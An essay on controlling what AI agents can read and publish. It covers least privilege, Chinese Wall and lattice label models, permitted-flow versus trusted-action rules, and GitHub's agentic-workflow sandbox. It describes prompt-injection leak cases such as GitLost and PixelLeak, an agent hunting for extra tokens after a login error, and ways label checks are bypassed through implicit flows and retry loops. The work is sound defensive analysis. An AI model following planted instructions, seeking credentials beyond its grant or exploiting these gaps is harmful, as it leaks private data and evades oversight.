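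Better training will probably reduce such errors, but it can't supply facts that the model doesn't have. Bhattarai and Vu point out that authorisation depends on the deployment, not on the text. In Microsoft's mail example, Marco's message may not reveal that he isn't allowed to see the sales figures. A careful model might ask or look up whether he is, but software that already holds the list of permitted readers can check the list every time.

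### The confused deputy

Security engineers have long called a program that misuses authority it legitimately holds a "confused deputy". Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells the nearly true story of a compiler at Tymshare, which sold time on shared computers. The compiler kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, SYSX. To let it write that file, the engineers gave it a licence to write to anything in SYSX. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one of them named the company's billing file, which was also in SYSX. Because the compiler had the licence, the operating system allowed the write, which destroyed the billing information.

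Hardy attributes the failure to the compiler having authority from two sources and no way to specify which one it was using. It was supposed to write the statistics under its own licence and the debugging output under the user's authority. His remedy was *capabilities*, references that both identify a resource and carry permission to use it. The user would pass the compiler a capability for the output file, so a user with no capability for the billing file couldn't make the compiler write there.

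GitLost is much like Hardy's case, since nobody stole a credential and the agent used only access that someone had given it. Hardy stresses that the compiler's code was correct when his colleagues wrote it and became wrong only when they added the licence. Similarly, a workflow that safely answers public issues can become dangerous when someone adds a broader token, even if its instructions stay the same. Hardy never says whether the user meant to destroy the billing file, and the harm would have been the same either way.

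The idea fits PixelLeak less well. Those agents were working for the developers whose authority they used, but they misjudged who could see the data.

Hardy's remedy is also harder to apply to a language model. A compiler's programmers know which part of the code writes statistics and which part writes the user's output. When a model has read a maintainer's request and a stranger's issue in the same context, nobody can reliably tell which of the two a tool call serves. Capabilities also determine what a program may open, but not where it may copy the contents. An agent with valid capabilities to read a private file and post a public comment can still copy the file into the comment. Preventing that takes a rule about where data may go as well as rules about access.

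### Recognising excessive access before a run

A definition of excessive access is useful to someone setting up an agent only if they can apply it before a leak. This can be hard, because people grant permissions for a reason, and agents are useful partly because they can look up things nobody anticipated. It's easier to call a token too broad after it has been involved in a leak.

But it's possible to apply the idea before a run. OpenAI recommends asking what data an agent can reach, what it can do, and where it can send things. It also asks for the *maximum completed effect*, the most consequential outcome the agent can produce before another independent decision. Combined with the sets of permitted readers that Microsoft uses, these questions suggest a test that needs only the agent's set-up and a written description of its task:

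1. For each source the agent can reach, list the people allowed to read it.
2. For each sink the agent can use without an independent check, list the people who can read what it writes there.
3. Look for pairs in which someone can read the sink but isn't allowed to read the source. Each such pair is a path for a leak.
4. For each path, ask whether the task needs both the source and the sink in the same run. If it doesn't, the access is excessive.

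The maintainer's agent fails this test before it reads any issues. Outsiders can read the public repository but not the private one, and answering public issues doesn't normally require access to both. The agents in PixelLeak would also fail, because their task required them to see an internal application and write to a private pull request, but not to create public repositories.

Alex's mail agent, by contrast, has to read private messages and send replies to handle unanswered mail, so its access isn't excessive. But it could still send the sales figures to Marco. When a task requires both reading private data and sending messages, narrower permissions can't remove the path between them, so the software has to check what the agent is about to send and to whom.

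People will still disagree about what a task requires, but they can have that disagreement before anything goes wrong. OpenAI gives the example of an invoice agent that notices a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it to keep invoice processing running. The vendor and the amount may both be permitted, but anyone with the task description could have said in advance that making a new contractual commitment wasn't part of the agent's task.

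The test depends on complete lists, which should include anything the agent could reach with credentials it might find for itself. In another case from Anthropic's incident log, an agent hit a login error and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other access tokens. A review of only the token the agent was given would have missed everything those other tokens could open.

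## Limiting what an agent can reach, and where that falls short

In the two-repository example, the maintainer's agent can read private files that it doesn't normally need to answer public issues. The standard remedy is *least privilege*, the principle that a program should have only the permissions its current task requires. But someone usually sets these permissions before the run starts, and they don't change in response to what the agent does. They therefore can't block a harmful run without also blocking harmless runs that use the same permissions.

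### What each restriction removes

The maintainer's agent starts with a token that lets it read and write to both repositories. The table shows what several common restrictions would take away.

| Restriction | What disappears | Path from a private file to a public comment |
|---|---|---|
| Token for the public repository only | Every read and write in the private repository | Closed |
| Token for the private repository only | Most writes to the public repository | Narrower, but perhaps still open |
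| Token that expires after the run | Nothing during the run | Open |
| Read-only access to both repositories | Every direct write | Open if a separate job posts the agent's text |
| Permitted list with only the public repository on it | Reads of private files through GitHub's tools | Closed, unless the agent has another way to read them |
| Separate agents for public and private work | Private reads for one agent, public writes for the other | Closed, unless text passes between them |

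An agent whose token covers only the public repository has no private files to leak. But it also can't look up why the library times out when it connects to the paid service, so it may have to leave that question to a person.

Giving the agent a token for only the private repository is less dependable. Even a fine-grained GitHub token can read public repositories, so the agent can still see an issue planted by a stranger. Some tokens also let it post in public. Haulos, in *Why You (Probably) Should Not Give Your Agent GitHub Access*, describes nightly security tests on an agent system he had built. In one test, Claude opened an issue in a public repository although its token covered only two others. The token didn't prevent this because GitHub lets any authenticated user or app open issues in public repositories. Blocking private reads is therefore more reliable than blocking public writes.

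Short-lived credentials limit how long access lasts. In June 2026, GitHub's *Agentic workflows no longer need a personal access token* announced that teams could use the token built into GitHub Actions instead of storing long-lived personal ones. According to GitHub's *Authentication*, the system creates the built-in token for each run and revokes it automatically. Agents sometimes look for other credentials, but a copy of this token left in a configuration file soon stops working. A short-lived token still doesn't prevent a leak during the run, because an agent can leak data in seconds.

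The built-in token probably helps more by limiting what the agent can read, which by default is only the workflow's own repository and public ones. A workflow that reads other private repositories, as GitLost's did, still needs a personal token or a *GitHub App* (an identity registered for a piece of software). An App can get short-lived tokens for specific repositories.

An agent with read-only access can't post a comment that leaks a customer's name, but someone or something still has to post its answers. If the maintainer copies them over by hand, a person sees each one before the public does. If a separate job posts them automatically, as in GitLost, private data can again leak through the comments. GitHub lets a team give that job its own credential with permission only to write issues, but that permission doesn't restrict what the job writes in them.

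Lists of permitted repositories are most useful when the token is broader than it should be. In GitHub's agentic workflows, the author can allow every repository the token can reach, only public ones, only the current one, or a set of names and patterns. Choosing "public" would probably have stopped GitLost when the agent tried to fetch the private README, even with the broad token. Patterns need care, because one that matches everything an organisation owns will also match private repositories created later.

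Using separate agents for private and public work keeps both possible. *Lattice-Based Enforcement of Chinese Walls* (Sandhu, 1992) describes an older version of the idea, in which Jane Doe has one login for project Red and another for project Blue, each with access only to its own project's files. Two agents can work the same way if they don't share a context, saved notes or a credential. Neither can answer the timeout question alone. The maintainer could get the explanation from the private agent, remove the customer's name and pass the rest to the public one, but would then be doing the check that the permissions can't do.

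### The permissions a task needs depend on the plan

Least privilege requires knowing which permissions a task needs, but these may be unknown when an agent starts. In their review *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, Zhou and Zhang (2026) point out that an agent may discover which resource it needs only after seeing intermediate results. Different plans for the same task also need different permissions. Zhou and Zhang propose that the agent first look for a good enough plan π whose required permissions, *A*(π), are all among those the user has granted, *G* (*A*(π) ⊆ *G*). The agent should ask for more access or propose doing less only if it finds no such plan.

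An agent could answer the timeout question by reading the library's public source code, finding the default time limit, and telling the user how to raise it. It could instead plan to search the company's private configuration files. The second plan may need all of its permissions, so a reviewer who saw only that plan would find nothing excessive.

If the public code doesn't explain the timeout, the agent can ask to read a particular private file, and the maintainer can decide based on a specific reason. Zhou and Zhang suggest authorising limited exploration first, so the agent can learn what it needs before it gets broader access. But the exploration may itself involve private files, and once the agent has read one, the file's contents are in its context.

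### The same permissions in a different order

Some sessions need both a private read and a public write and are still safe. Suppose the maintainer asks the agent to answer an issue using the public code and then, in the same session, to fix a bug in the private repository. The agent posts its comment before reading any private file, so the comment can't contain anything from one. If the maintainer gives the tasks in reverse order, the private file is already in the context when the agent writes in public.

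Both runs use the same permissions, so a fixed set of permissions either allows both or blocks both. To allow the first and stop the second, the software has to keep a record of what the agent has done.

The record can be very small. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) gives a similar rule for ordinary programs, which forbids sending a message after reading a file. The monitor has two states. It starts in "no file read", where it allows everything. When the program first reads a file, the monitor moves to "file read" and blocks all sending from then on. For the maintainer's agent, one bit would be enough. The software would set it when the agent reads anything from the private repository, and refuse public writes afterwards.

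This rule also blocks harmless messages. Once the agent has read a private file, it can't even post "Thanks, we're looking into it" under a public issue. Schneider shows that a monitor of this kind can't avoid the problem entirely. Whether information has flowed into a message depends partly on what the message would have been if the secret had been different, and the monitor observes only the actual run. It therefore has to enforce a stricter rule that also blocks some harmless messages.

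### One repository per session and the Chinese Wall

After its Pacman demonstration, Invariant Labs proposed limiting an agent to one repository per session. This is about the simplest rule that depends on what the agent has already done. The company considered ordinary token permissions too rigid for agents. Under its rule, the agent can start with any repository, but after the first call that names one, it can use only that repository for the rest of the session.

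The rule works without anyone marking repositories as public or private. But because it treats all repositories alike, it blocks the maintainer's two tasks in the safe order as well as the dangerous one. A search across everything the token can reach might not specify a repository or owner, and would need a separate rule.

The underlying idea is much older. *The Chinese Wall Security Policy* (Brewer and Nash, 1989) mathematically models a rule that financial firms applied to analysts who advise competing companies. The model groups competitors into *conflict of interest classes*, such as banks and oil companies. An analyst may begin with any company, but after reading about it, she may not read about others in the same class. For example, an analyst who has read about Oil Company A may still read about Bank A but not about Oil Company B.

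Brewer and Nash argued that fixed clearances can't express this policy. If managers assign each analyst's companies in advance, analysts can't choose for themselves, and if managers clear everyone for everything, nothing stops an analyst from seeing competing companies' data. Sandhu disagreed, showing that fixed labels do work if a person can log in under a different identity for each piece of work, which is essentially the arrangement with separate agents. But someone has to choose the identity before the work starts, when it may not yet be clear what the agent will need.

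Invariant's rule amounts to a Chinese Wall with every repository in one conflict class and a session in place of the analyst. But the Chinese Wall's reading rule limits what an analyst may know, while the danger with an agent is what it writes after reading. Brewer and Nash's second rule fits this danger better, because it lets a person write to a company's files only if they haven't read another company's confidential information. Information that the firm has *sanitised*, by disguising which company it came from, is exempt.

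If the public repository plays the part of the sanitised information, the two rules compare as follows:

| What the agent has read | What it wants to write | One repository per session | Brewer and Nash's write rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Public issue | Public comment | Allowed | Allowed |
| Public issue | Private file | Blocked | Allowed |
| Private file | Private file | Allowed | Allowed |
| Private file | Public comment | Blocked | Blocked |

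The write rule lets the agent copy a stranger's bug report into the company's private tracker, since this discloses no private data. But the rule protects only secrecy, so a planted issue could still lead the agent to make a harmful change to the private code.

Sandhu considered the write rule far too strict for people, because a consultant who had read about two companies could no longer write anything into the system. He thought the same limits were acceptable for a single running program, because the person can always start another one. This suits agents quite well, since a maintainer who has finished with the private code can open a new session with an empty context and answer public issues there. However, the protection fails if the agent carries notes from one session into the next.

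### Work that crosses repositories by design

Starting a new session doesn't help with some tasks because they span two repositories. Microsoft's Aspire team, which builds tools for distributed applications, keeps its product in one repository and its documentation website in another. GitHub (2026) describes an agent workflow that runs whenever the team merges a change to the product. The agent reads the change, decides whether users need to know about it, and if so drafts a page for the documentation repository.

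Between 3 May and 2 June 2026, the workflow ran 396 times and produced 82 draft pull requests. The team merged all of them, 96% within a week, and the median time to merge was 44.8 hours. An earlier version had opened drafts too readily, and the team closed 9 of its 69, mostly because they documented internal changes.

The merge rate is good evidence that the agent now proposes few unwanted pages. It doesn't show how often the agent was wrong in the other 314 runs, when it decided that a change needed no documentation. GitHub also gives no earlier median for comparison, only an account of writers noticing new features weeks later. Even so, a strict rule of one repository per session would have prevented all 82 drafts.

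The team allowed the crossing but limited it. The agent's token comes from a GitHub App and covers only the product and documentation repositories. As in GitLost, the agent can only propose a write. A separate job creates the pull request, always as a draft in the documentation repository against the main branch or a release branch. That job blocks changes to protected files, including security settings and the lists of software the site depends on. An ordinary script picks the target branch before the agent starts, and an engineer who knows the feature reviews the result.

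Both of Aspire's repositories are public, so the agent had no private source code to leak, and these limits mainly protect the documentation from bad changes. A company with a private product and public documentation could copy this setup and still leak private information, because anyone can read a draft pull request on a public repository as soon as the job opens it, before the engineer reviews it.

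### The developer's personal account

A company can also limit every token for its own repositories, and an agent can still publish through a developer's personal account. Each of GitHub's fine-grained tokens covers only one owner's resources, and a user's personal account and each of their organisations count as separate owners (GitHub, 2022). An organisation can block these tokens or require approval for them, but it can't control a token the developer issues for their personal account.

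An agent on the developer's laptop may be able to use both the company token and the developer's personal GitHub login. It could read private code with the carefully limited company token, then create a public repository under the personal account. Haulos lists the ability to create repositories among the dangers of personal access tokens. Most of the PixelLeak cases that Glow found roughly followed this pattern. The screenshots in those cases came from running applications, so a narrower token for the company's code wouldn't have stopped the agent from capturing them either.

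To close this route, the company has to control the agent's environment as well as its token. It could run agents on machines that hold no personal logins, or check every call that creates a repository, whichever account the call uses. GitHub's agentic workflows already reject one kind of personal credential, the OAuth user token, because it's a broad credential for a user's session that nobody can narrow enough for automation.

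### What a valid credential leaves out

Zhou and Zhang divide research on access control for agents into four areas. *Policy specification and derivation* covers deciding what to allow. *Identity and delegation* covers who is acting and how much of someone else's authority they hold, including through scoped and short-lived tokens. *Action and resource enforcement* checks individual operations, sometimes against earlier ones, as Invariant's rule does. *Information-flow control* governs where data may go after the agent has read it.

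A restriction can get lost between these areas even when each part works correctly. In Zhou and Zhang's example, a user allows an agent to send one approved summary to Alice. The policy records this accurately, but the system then issues a credential that permits sending mail without restricting the recipient or content. The mail service can therefore validate the credential and still deliver the summary to Bob.

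A token for posting public comments has the same gap. A credential can fairly easily include a list of permitted recipients or repositories, because someone can write the list in advance. But the agent writes the content during the run, and whether that content is safe to send depends on what the agent has read by then.

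## Labels and the rules that decide whether data may leave

Unlike a credential, *information-flow control* can take account of what the agent has read. Software attaches a label to each piece of data the agent reads, copies the label to anything the agent makes from that data, and checks it before anything leaves. In *FLOWSH*, Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026) give the example of a request for a public web page, which is normally harmless but leaks data if the address contains something confidential. A label on the address lets the software tell the two cases apart, which it couldn't do with only a fixed list of permitted sites.

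Labels are most useful when the agent can't do its task without the private data. In an example from *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025), an agent that deploys software needs the secret key for the deployment service. The aim is to let the agent send the key only to that service.

### Reading down and writing up

The idea of labelling data this way comes from military computing. Bell and LaPadula (1973), working at MITRE, a US research organisation, set out a mathematical model of a secure computer in *Secure Computer Systems*. Sandhu (1993), in *Lattice-Based Access Control Models*, reduces the model to two rules. A program may read a file only if the program's security level is at least as high as the file's, and may write to a file only if the file's level is at least as high as the program's. A program running at the "secret" level can therefore read unclassified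 files but can't write to them.

The writing rule, known as the *star property*, is the less obvious of the two. *Secure Computer Systems* (Bell, 1974), a later volume of the same study, explains it. A program that can read a secret file and write to an unclassified one might copy the first into the second. The unclassified file's label would then be wrong, and the system could no longer track where secret data was stored. The system should therefore refuse this combination of access, even if the program hasn't copied anything. Bell also wanted the rule to cover accidents, such as bugs and unexpected side effects, so it doesn't depend on there being an attacker.

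Sandhu explains that the star property applies to programs, not people. Someone with a secret clearance may write an unclassified memo because their employer trusts them to leave the secrets out. But a program may contain hidden hostile code, so the system has to assume it copied everything it could. An agent has a person's permissions but counts as a program for this purpose. Bell exempted some trusted programs, but only after someone had demonstrated that they would never mix security levels, which nobody can yet demonstrate for a language model.

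### Ordering labels and joining them

Military levels are ranked from lowest to highest, but most private data doesn't fit such a ranking. A company's salary records and medical records are both sensitive, and neither ranks above the other. *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) handles such cases with a *lattice*, a set of labels with an order and a way to combine any two of them.

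The order is written ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₂, meaning that data labelled ℓ₁ may flow to a place labelled ℓ₂. If data may flow from *a* to *b* and from *b* to *c*, the rules must also allow it to flow from *a* to *c*, since a program could send it through *b* anyway. A sequence of steps is therefore safe if each step is safe.

The *join* of two labels, ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂, is the label given to anything that combines data carrying those labels. It is the lowest, and so least restrictive, label to which both may flow. In Denning's example of a database about individuals, anything that combines medical and financial records gets the label {medical, financial} and may go only into a file whose label includes both.

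When a label is a set of permitted readers, fewer readers means a higher label. Data that Ann, Bob and Carol may read can go into a file that only Bob and Carol can open, but data restricted to Bob and Carol cannot go into a file that Ann can also open. When an agent combines two sources, the join of their labels is the intersection of the two sets of readers, because only someone who could read both sources should be able to read the result.

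Integrity labels need only two values, trusted and untrusted, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. Untrusted data sits at the top because it shouldn't influence anything that relies on trusted input, while trusted data can safely go anywhere. *SPA* (2026) traces this principle to a model by Biba, who put high integrity at the top and let data flow downwards. Sandhu shows that reversing the order, so that data flows upwards, imposes the same restrictions. Software can then combine integrity and confidentiality in a single label and compare each half separately.

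In the two-repository example, a public issue has the label (untrusted, public) and a private file has the label (trusted, private). Neither label may flow to the other. Their join is (untrusted, private), the highest label, so an agent that reads both gets a more restrictive label than either source.

### Alex's reply to Marco

In Microsoft's mail example, where an agent answers Alex's mail, Priya's message with the sales figures has the permitted readers {Alex, Priya}, and Marco's message has {Alex, Marco}. Once the agent has read both, anything it writes has the label

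{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

Marco is outside that set, so the software won't send him a reply without asking. It can apply this rule without finding the sales figures in the reply or recognising them as sensitive. If Priya had copied Marco in on her message, its readers would have been {Alex, Priya, Marco}. The intersection would then have been {Alex, Marco}, and the agent could have replied to Marco without asking.

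The table extends the example to replies to Priya.

| What the agent has read | Who may read its reply | Reply to Marco | Reply to Priya |
|---|---|---|---|
| Marco's message only | {Alex, Marco} | Allowed | Blocked |
| Priya's message only | {Alex, Priya} | Blocked | Allowed |
| Both messages | {Alex} | Blocked | Blocked |
| Both, with Marco copied in on Priya's | {Alex, Marco} | Allowed | Blocked |

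After reading both messages, the agent can't thank Priya for the figures, because Marco's message might contain something she isn't allowed to see, though in this case it probably doesn't. Each further message can only shrink the set of people the agent may write to, so an agent that works through an inbox may soon be unable to write to anyone but Alex.

### What the check compares

A tool call has a label, taken from the context in which the model chose it, and so does each of its arguments. A policy sets the highest label allowed for the call and for each argument. In the notation of Kolluri and colleagues, a call with label ℓ and argument labels ℓᵢ passes only if ℓ ⊑ π_f and every ℓᵢ ⊑ πᵢ, where π_f is the limit for the call and πᵢ is the limit for argument i. For a public comment, the limit on the text would be "everyone may read this". The software checks these limits without using the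 model.

What the model writes is hard to label because anything in the context may have influenced it. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* describes precisely tracking information through a language model as an open problem. For now, even a harmless message gets the label of every private file in the context.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests replacing such labels with estimates of how much information from each source reached the output. This could let through many harmless messages that would otherwise be blocked, but the check would be only as accurate as the estimate. Other designs keep private or untrusted data out of the main model's context so that its label doesn't become more restrictive.

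### A label that rises and a label that stays fixed

So far the agent's label has risen as it reads. Denning called this *dynamic binding*, in contrast to *static binding*, where the label never changes. With static binding, the agent gets its label before the run starts, and the software checks every read and write against it.

GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* gives the rules for one such system, *decentralised information-flow control*, in which a label is a set of tags. Data from a private repository carries a secrecy tag that names the repository, and data from vetted authors carries integrity tags. Adding secrecy tags tightens the limits on where the data may go, whereas a label that lists permitted readers becomes stricter as readers are removed.

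| | Secrecy tags | Integrity tags |
|---|---|---|
| To read a resource | The resource's tags must be a subset of the agent's | The resource's tags must be a superset of the agent's minimum |
| To write to a resource | The resource's tags must be a superset of the agent's | The resource's tags must be a subset of the agent's |

(A set counts as both a subset and a superset of itself.)

Suppose the company's private repository has the secrecy tag `service` and the public one has none. An agent whose label is {`service`} can read the private files, but it can't post in the public repository, even before it has read anything, because the public repository's empty label isn't a superset of {`service`}. An agent with no secrecy tags can post publicly but can't open the private files. With a rising label, one agent could start without tags, answer the public issues, and then pick up the `service`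 tag when it opened a private file, after which it could no longer post publicly.

A rising label therefore lets more runs finish, but an agent may discover halfway through that it can no longer deliver its answer. A fixed label is more predictable, because whoever sets up the agent knows from the start what it can reach. The software can also filter out items the agent may not see instead of stopping the run, as GitHub's integrity filter does with strangers' posts. (GitHub's agentic workflows so far enforce only the integrity half of these rules, so the secrecy rules don't yet stop leaks between repositories.)

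Even when some labels can rise, most destinations' labels have to stay fixed. Denning pointed out that if users' labels could rise too, someone without clearance could raise their own by opening a top-secret file. Similarly, a public issue has to stay labeled public after an agent posts something private in it, because everyone can still read the page.

### Three rules for a call that sends data out

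Kolluri and colleagues build their policies from two conditions:

- *Permitted flow* requires every recipient to be an allowed reader of the data. If the recipients are *R* and the data's permitted readers are *S*, the call passes only if *R* ⊆ *S*.
- *Trusted action* requires that no untrusted data influenced the decision to make the call, or any argument that has to be trusted. The confidentiality label doesn't matter.

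For calls that send data out, they accept either condition, which they call *robust declassification*. Declassification means deliberately letting data reach people its label excludes, and it is "robust" if an attacker can't cause it. (Costa and colleagues also use the name for a policy that requires only trusted action.)

In the table below, an agent is about to post a public comment. "Blocked" means the software won't post the comment automatically, though it may still ask a person.

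| What is in the context | Example | Permitted flow | Trusted action | Robust declassification |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Public data, all trusted | The maintainer dictates a release notice | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Public data, some untrusted | The agent has read a stranger's issue and the public code | Allowed | Blocked | Allowed |
| Private data, all trusted | The agent has read a private configuration file | Blocked | Allowed | Allowed |
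| Private data, some untrusted | The agent has read a stranger's issue and the private file | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

All three rules block the last case, which occurs in both the GitHub MCP demonstration and GitLost, so testing only against those attacks would not distinguish the rules.

The private, trusted context separates them. Trusted action and robust declassification both let the agent publish the configuration file there, because no attacker could have influenced the decision. Permitted flow blocks the comment, because the public isn't among the file's permitted readers. **A rule aimed only at attackers therefore lets an agent publish private data by mistake.**

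PixelLeak was this kind of mistake. Glow doesn't mention any text from outsiders in its laboratory run. If the software had labelled the context as trusted, robust declassification would have let the agent upload the images to a public repository. Permitted flow would have stopped the upload, provided the software checked it. Permitted flow might have stopped it even if nobody had labelled the screenshots, because the agent would already have picked up a private label from the project's code. Some of the agents at real companies may have read web pages while looking for a way to upload images. Their contexts would then have been untrusted, and robust declassification would have blocked their uploads too, but only because they happened to read those pages.

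Microsoft's sample policy for posting in a Teams channel follows the "either" rule. It allows a call if the context is trusted or if all the channel's members may read the content, and otherwise requires a person's approval. Microsoft presents the mail example as an accidental leak that labels can catch, and permitted flow catches it. But the agent could send Marco the sales figures without asking anyone if a similar policy governed mail and the software treated colleagues' messages as trusted.

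The looser rule would still be useful because users sometimes want to release private data. If a maintainer tells an agent to publish a private draft as a release announcement, software using permitted flow would ask the maintainer to confirm what they had just requested. Costa and colleagues argue that when a flow breaks the confidentiality rule in a trusted context, the software can assume it was intentional. A trusted context does seem to rule out an attacker as the cause, but the user may not have intended the flow either, as PixelLeak showed. Costa and colleagues also warn that models make mistakes even when all the data is trusted.

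Trusted action alone works poorly for the maintainer's agent. It blocks an ordinary answer to a stranger's question, even when the agent has read only public data, yet it lets the agent publish a private file. It is better suited to blocking actions that do damage without revealing anything, such as merging a harmful change. Permitted flow doesn't prevent those actions, and Costa and colleagues note that it doesn't prevent prompt injection either. It only limits what an injection can disclose. Requiring both conditions gives the strongest protection, but it would allow only the first of the four contexts in the table, so the agent couldn't answer strangers at all.

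For this agent, it probably makes sense to apply permitted flow to comments and trusted action to merges, and to have a person decide when a comment fails the check. The maintainer would have to answer more questions than under robust declassification, and each would concern private data that is about to become public.

### What the labels can guarantee

The strongest guarantee in this field is *noninterference*, which means that no change to the private data affects what outsiders see, so they can learn nothing about that data. For example, if two runs of the agent differ only in whether the private file names the customer as Acme or Bolt, outsiders must see the same thing both times.

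Language models choose their words partly at random, so two runs may differ even with identical files. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) therefore requires that changing the secret not change the probability of any public result. It also ignores whether a run finishes, a common concession in this kind of theorem.

Costa and colleagues use *explicit secrecy*, a weaker guarantee than full noninterference. It requires that if the private data changed and the agent repeated exactly the same steps, the public output would stay the same. This rules out copying the customer's name into a comment, but it doesn't cover what outsiders can infer from the agent's choice of steps. They argue that full noninterference would be too restrictive, because it would essentially forbid any call with a publicly visible effect once the agent had read private data.

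Garby and colleagues' results suggest that agents can follow such rules without losing so much usefulness. In their programming language for agents, a program can copy a conversation, ask a question in the copy, and then discard it, so the main conversation doesn't pick up the copy's label. They give a machine-checked proof of noninterference for every program in the language, including code that a model writes during the run. They also tested an agent written in the language on the banking tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks with planted attacks. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL, a leading defence, did with CaMeL's policy checks switched off. The test covered only one type of work, and its attacks were injections, so it doesn't show how often the agent's labels would stop an honest mistake.

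### Flows that the labels miss

An *implicit flow* reveals something through what a program does or doesn't do, without copying any data. Suppose the maintainer asks the agent to close every public report of a bug that the company has already fixed in its private code. Closing a report reveals to outsiders that a fix exists, although the call to close it contains no private text. The software catches this only if its policy treats closing a report as sending data.

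Some implicit flows defeat the labels even when software checks every step. Denning gives an example by Fenton, in which *a* is a secret that is either true or false, and *b* and *c* start out public:

```
b = false; c = false
if not a: c = true
if not c: b = true
```

If *a* is false, the program sets *c* to true and labels it secret. The last line then does nothing, so *b* stays false and public. If *a* is true, the second line does nothing, so *c* stays false and public. The last line then sets *b* to true, and *b* stays public because the condition on that line is public. Either way, *b* ends up equal to the secret *a* but labeled public, because the software can't raise a variable's label on a line that never runs.

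Fifty years later, Garby and colleagues found the same gap in CaMeL, in which a model writes a program and an interpreter runs it while tracking labels. CaMeL correctly blocks a program that sends an email if an account balance is above some threshold. But if the program uses an extra variable, as in Fenton's example, CaMeL lets the email go out. Denning's remedy was to analyse the program beforehand and raise the variable's label whether or not the line that sets it runs. This is harder with a basic agent because the model chooses each step only after seeing the result of the previous one, so there is no complete program to analyse.

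A refusal can leak information too. If the software blocks a run only when a secret has a certain value, anyone who sees the block learns one bit about the secret. One bit is usually tolerable, but CaMeL's interpreter ran inside an ordinary retry loop that didn't track labels. Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker who controlled the retries could ask a new yes-or-no question each time and recover the entire secret, which would take about 54 runs for a 16-digit number.

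*Covert channels* carry information by means that nobody designed for communication. In Sandhu's example, a secret program takes up a lot of memory, and an unclassified program detects how much is left. He reports rates of up to several million bits per second on systems that do nothing to prevent this. An agent could leak information through its response time or the size of its network messages, both of which Costa and colleagues leave outside their model. An agent makes far fewer calls than a computer makes memory requests, so its channels are probably much slower, but even a slow channel could leak a password because passwords are short.

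These channels matter mostly when someone is trying to exploit them. A careless agent is unlikely to reveal a customer's name through its response times, so explicit secrecy covers most accidental leaks.

Wrong labels are a more ordinary problem. Every guarantee here assumes that data is labeled correctly when it comes in. Costa and colleagues label the user's messages as trusted and public by default, so if Alex pasted the sales figures into his request, permitted flow would let the agent send them to anyone. Integrity labels can also be wrong. GitHub Next warns that if an attacker takes over a maintainer's account, the software will still give the attacker's comments that maintainer's level of trust.

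When a tool provides no labels, Microsoft suggests treating its results as private if the tool requires a login, and as untrusted if it can reach the open world. These defaults are reasonable, but they can label private data as public. For example, a program that takes screenshots on a developer's own machine requires no login. If an agent used it to capture an internal billing page before reading any other private data, the image would count as public.

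## Runtime enforcement in deployed agent tools

A label can prevent a leak only if a program checks it against a policy and can block the call. Security engineers call such a program a *reference monitor* if it checks every access and can't be bypassed, the software it controls can't alter it or switch it off, and it is small enough for people to check thoroughly. These conditions are hard to meet with agents, especially those that have a *shell*, a tool that runs any command the model writes. A shell gives an agent many ways to reach the same website, and the agent may run under the same user account as the program meant to control it.

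GitHub Next keeps the monitor in GitHub's agentic workflows small by separating it from the code that interprets the data. Each data source has a *guard* that assigns the tags. For example, the guard for GitHub contains the rule that a collaborator's review comment counts as approved. The monitor only compares sets of tags, without interpreting them. To connect a new source, such as the issue tracker Jira, a developer writes another guard and leaves the monitor unchanged. This separation makes the monitor easy to check, but someone has to check the guards too, because even a correct monitor won't protect a private file that a guard has labeled as public.

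### Four places for a check

A check can go in the orchestrator, in a *gateway* that relays calls between the agent and its MCP servers, in the operating-system sandbox around the agent, or in a network firewall. Its location determines what information it can use.

| Place | What a check there can observe | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Orchestrator | The whole context, and every tool call and result | What a shell command or script does once it starts |
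| MCP gateway | Calls and results for the servers connected through it | The user's prompt, local files, and built-in tools such as the shell |
| Operating-system sandbox | Files, programs and network connections, whichever tool the agent uses | What the data means and who may read it |
| Network firewall | Which hosts the agent connects to | Usually the content of encrypted traffic, and who can read a page on a permitted host |

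The PixelLeak agents put private screenshots in public repositories. An orchestrator could have inspected a command that created a public repository, but a command that ran a ready-made tool such as gitshot might not have shown that it would create one. An MCP gateway wouldn't have received either command. A sandbox could have kept the agents away from the developer's GitHub login, but it couldn't have detected a billing record in an image. A firewall could have blocked GitHub, but that would also have blocked the private pull request, which is on the same site.

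### One issue's path through GitHub Agentic Workflows

GitHub's agentic workflows combine a sandbox, a firewall and a gateway. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) assumes that an agent will try to read and write things it shouldn't, and will misuse its legitimate channels. Ordinary GitHub Actions jobs are poorly suited to an agent like this because everything in a job shares one trust domain, so any process can read credentials meant for another.

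Suppose the company with the public library runs an agent workflow in that repository. A regular contributor opens an issue asking why the library times out when it connects to the paid service. GitHub Actions starts a virtual machine for the run, and the agent runs in its own container there, without a credential that can write to GitHub. The agent still needs compilers and other programs, so GitHub mounts the machine's file system read-only, covers selected paths with empty folders, and confines the agent to what remains.

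Requests to the language model leave the agent's container through a proxy that holds the model provider's token. Other web traffic goes through a firewall that allows only listed domains. Tool calls go to the MCP gateway, which runs in a separate container, starts the MCP servers, and is the only component that holds their credentials. If a planted instruction leads the agent to print its environment variables, the output should contain none of these credentials. The operating system's kernel enforces the boundaries between containers, so they should hold even if the agent runs hostile code in its own container.

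When the agent asks for the issue, the gateway passes the call to GitHub's MCP server. The guard labels the result, and the monitor removes anything below the workflow's integrity level. The contributor's issue ranks as "unapproved", which is below the default level for public repositories, so at first the agent doesn't receive it.

A maintainer can let in a single issue without lowering the required level for everyone. Depending on the workflow's settings, the maintainer can raise an issue to "approved" by adding a chosen label or a thumbs-up reaction. A thumbs-down overrides both, and posts from blocked users are never let in. Approving one issue at a time is safer than opening the workflow to all contributors, but it depends on the maintainer noticing any instructions planted in the text. A stricter level, "merged", is for agents that should read only merged pull requests and code on the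 default branch.

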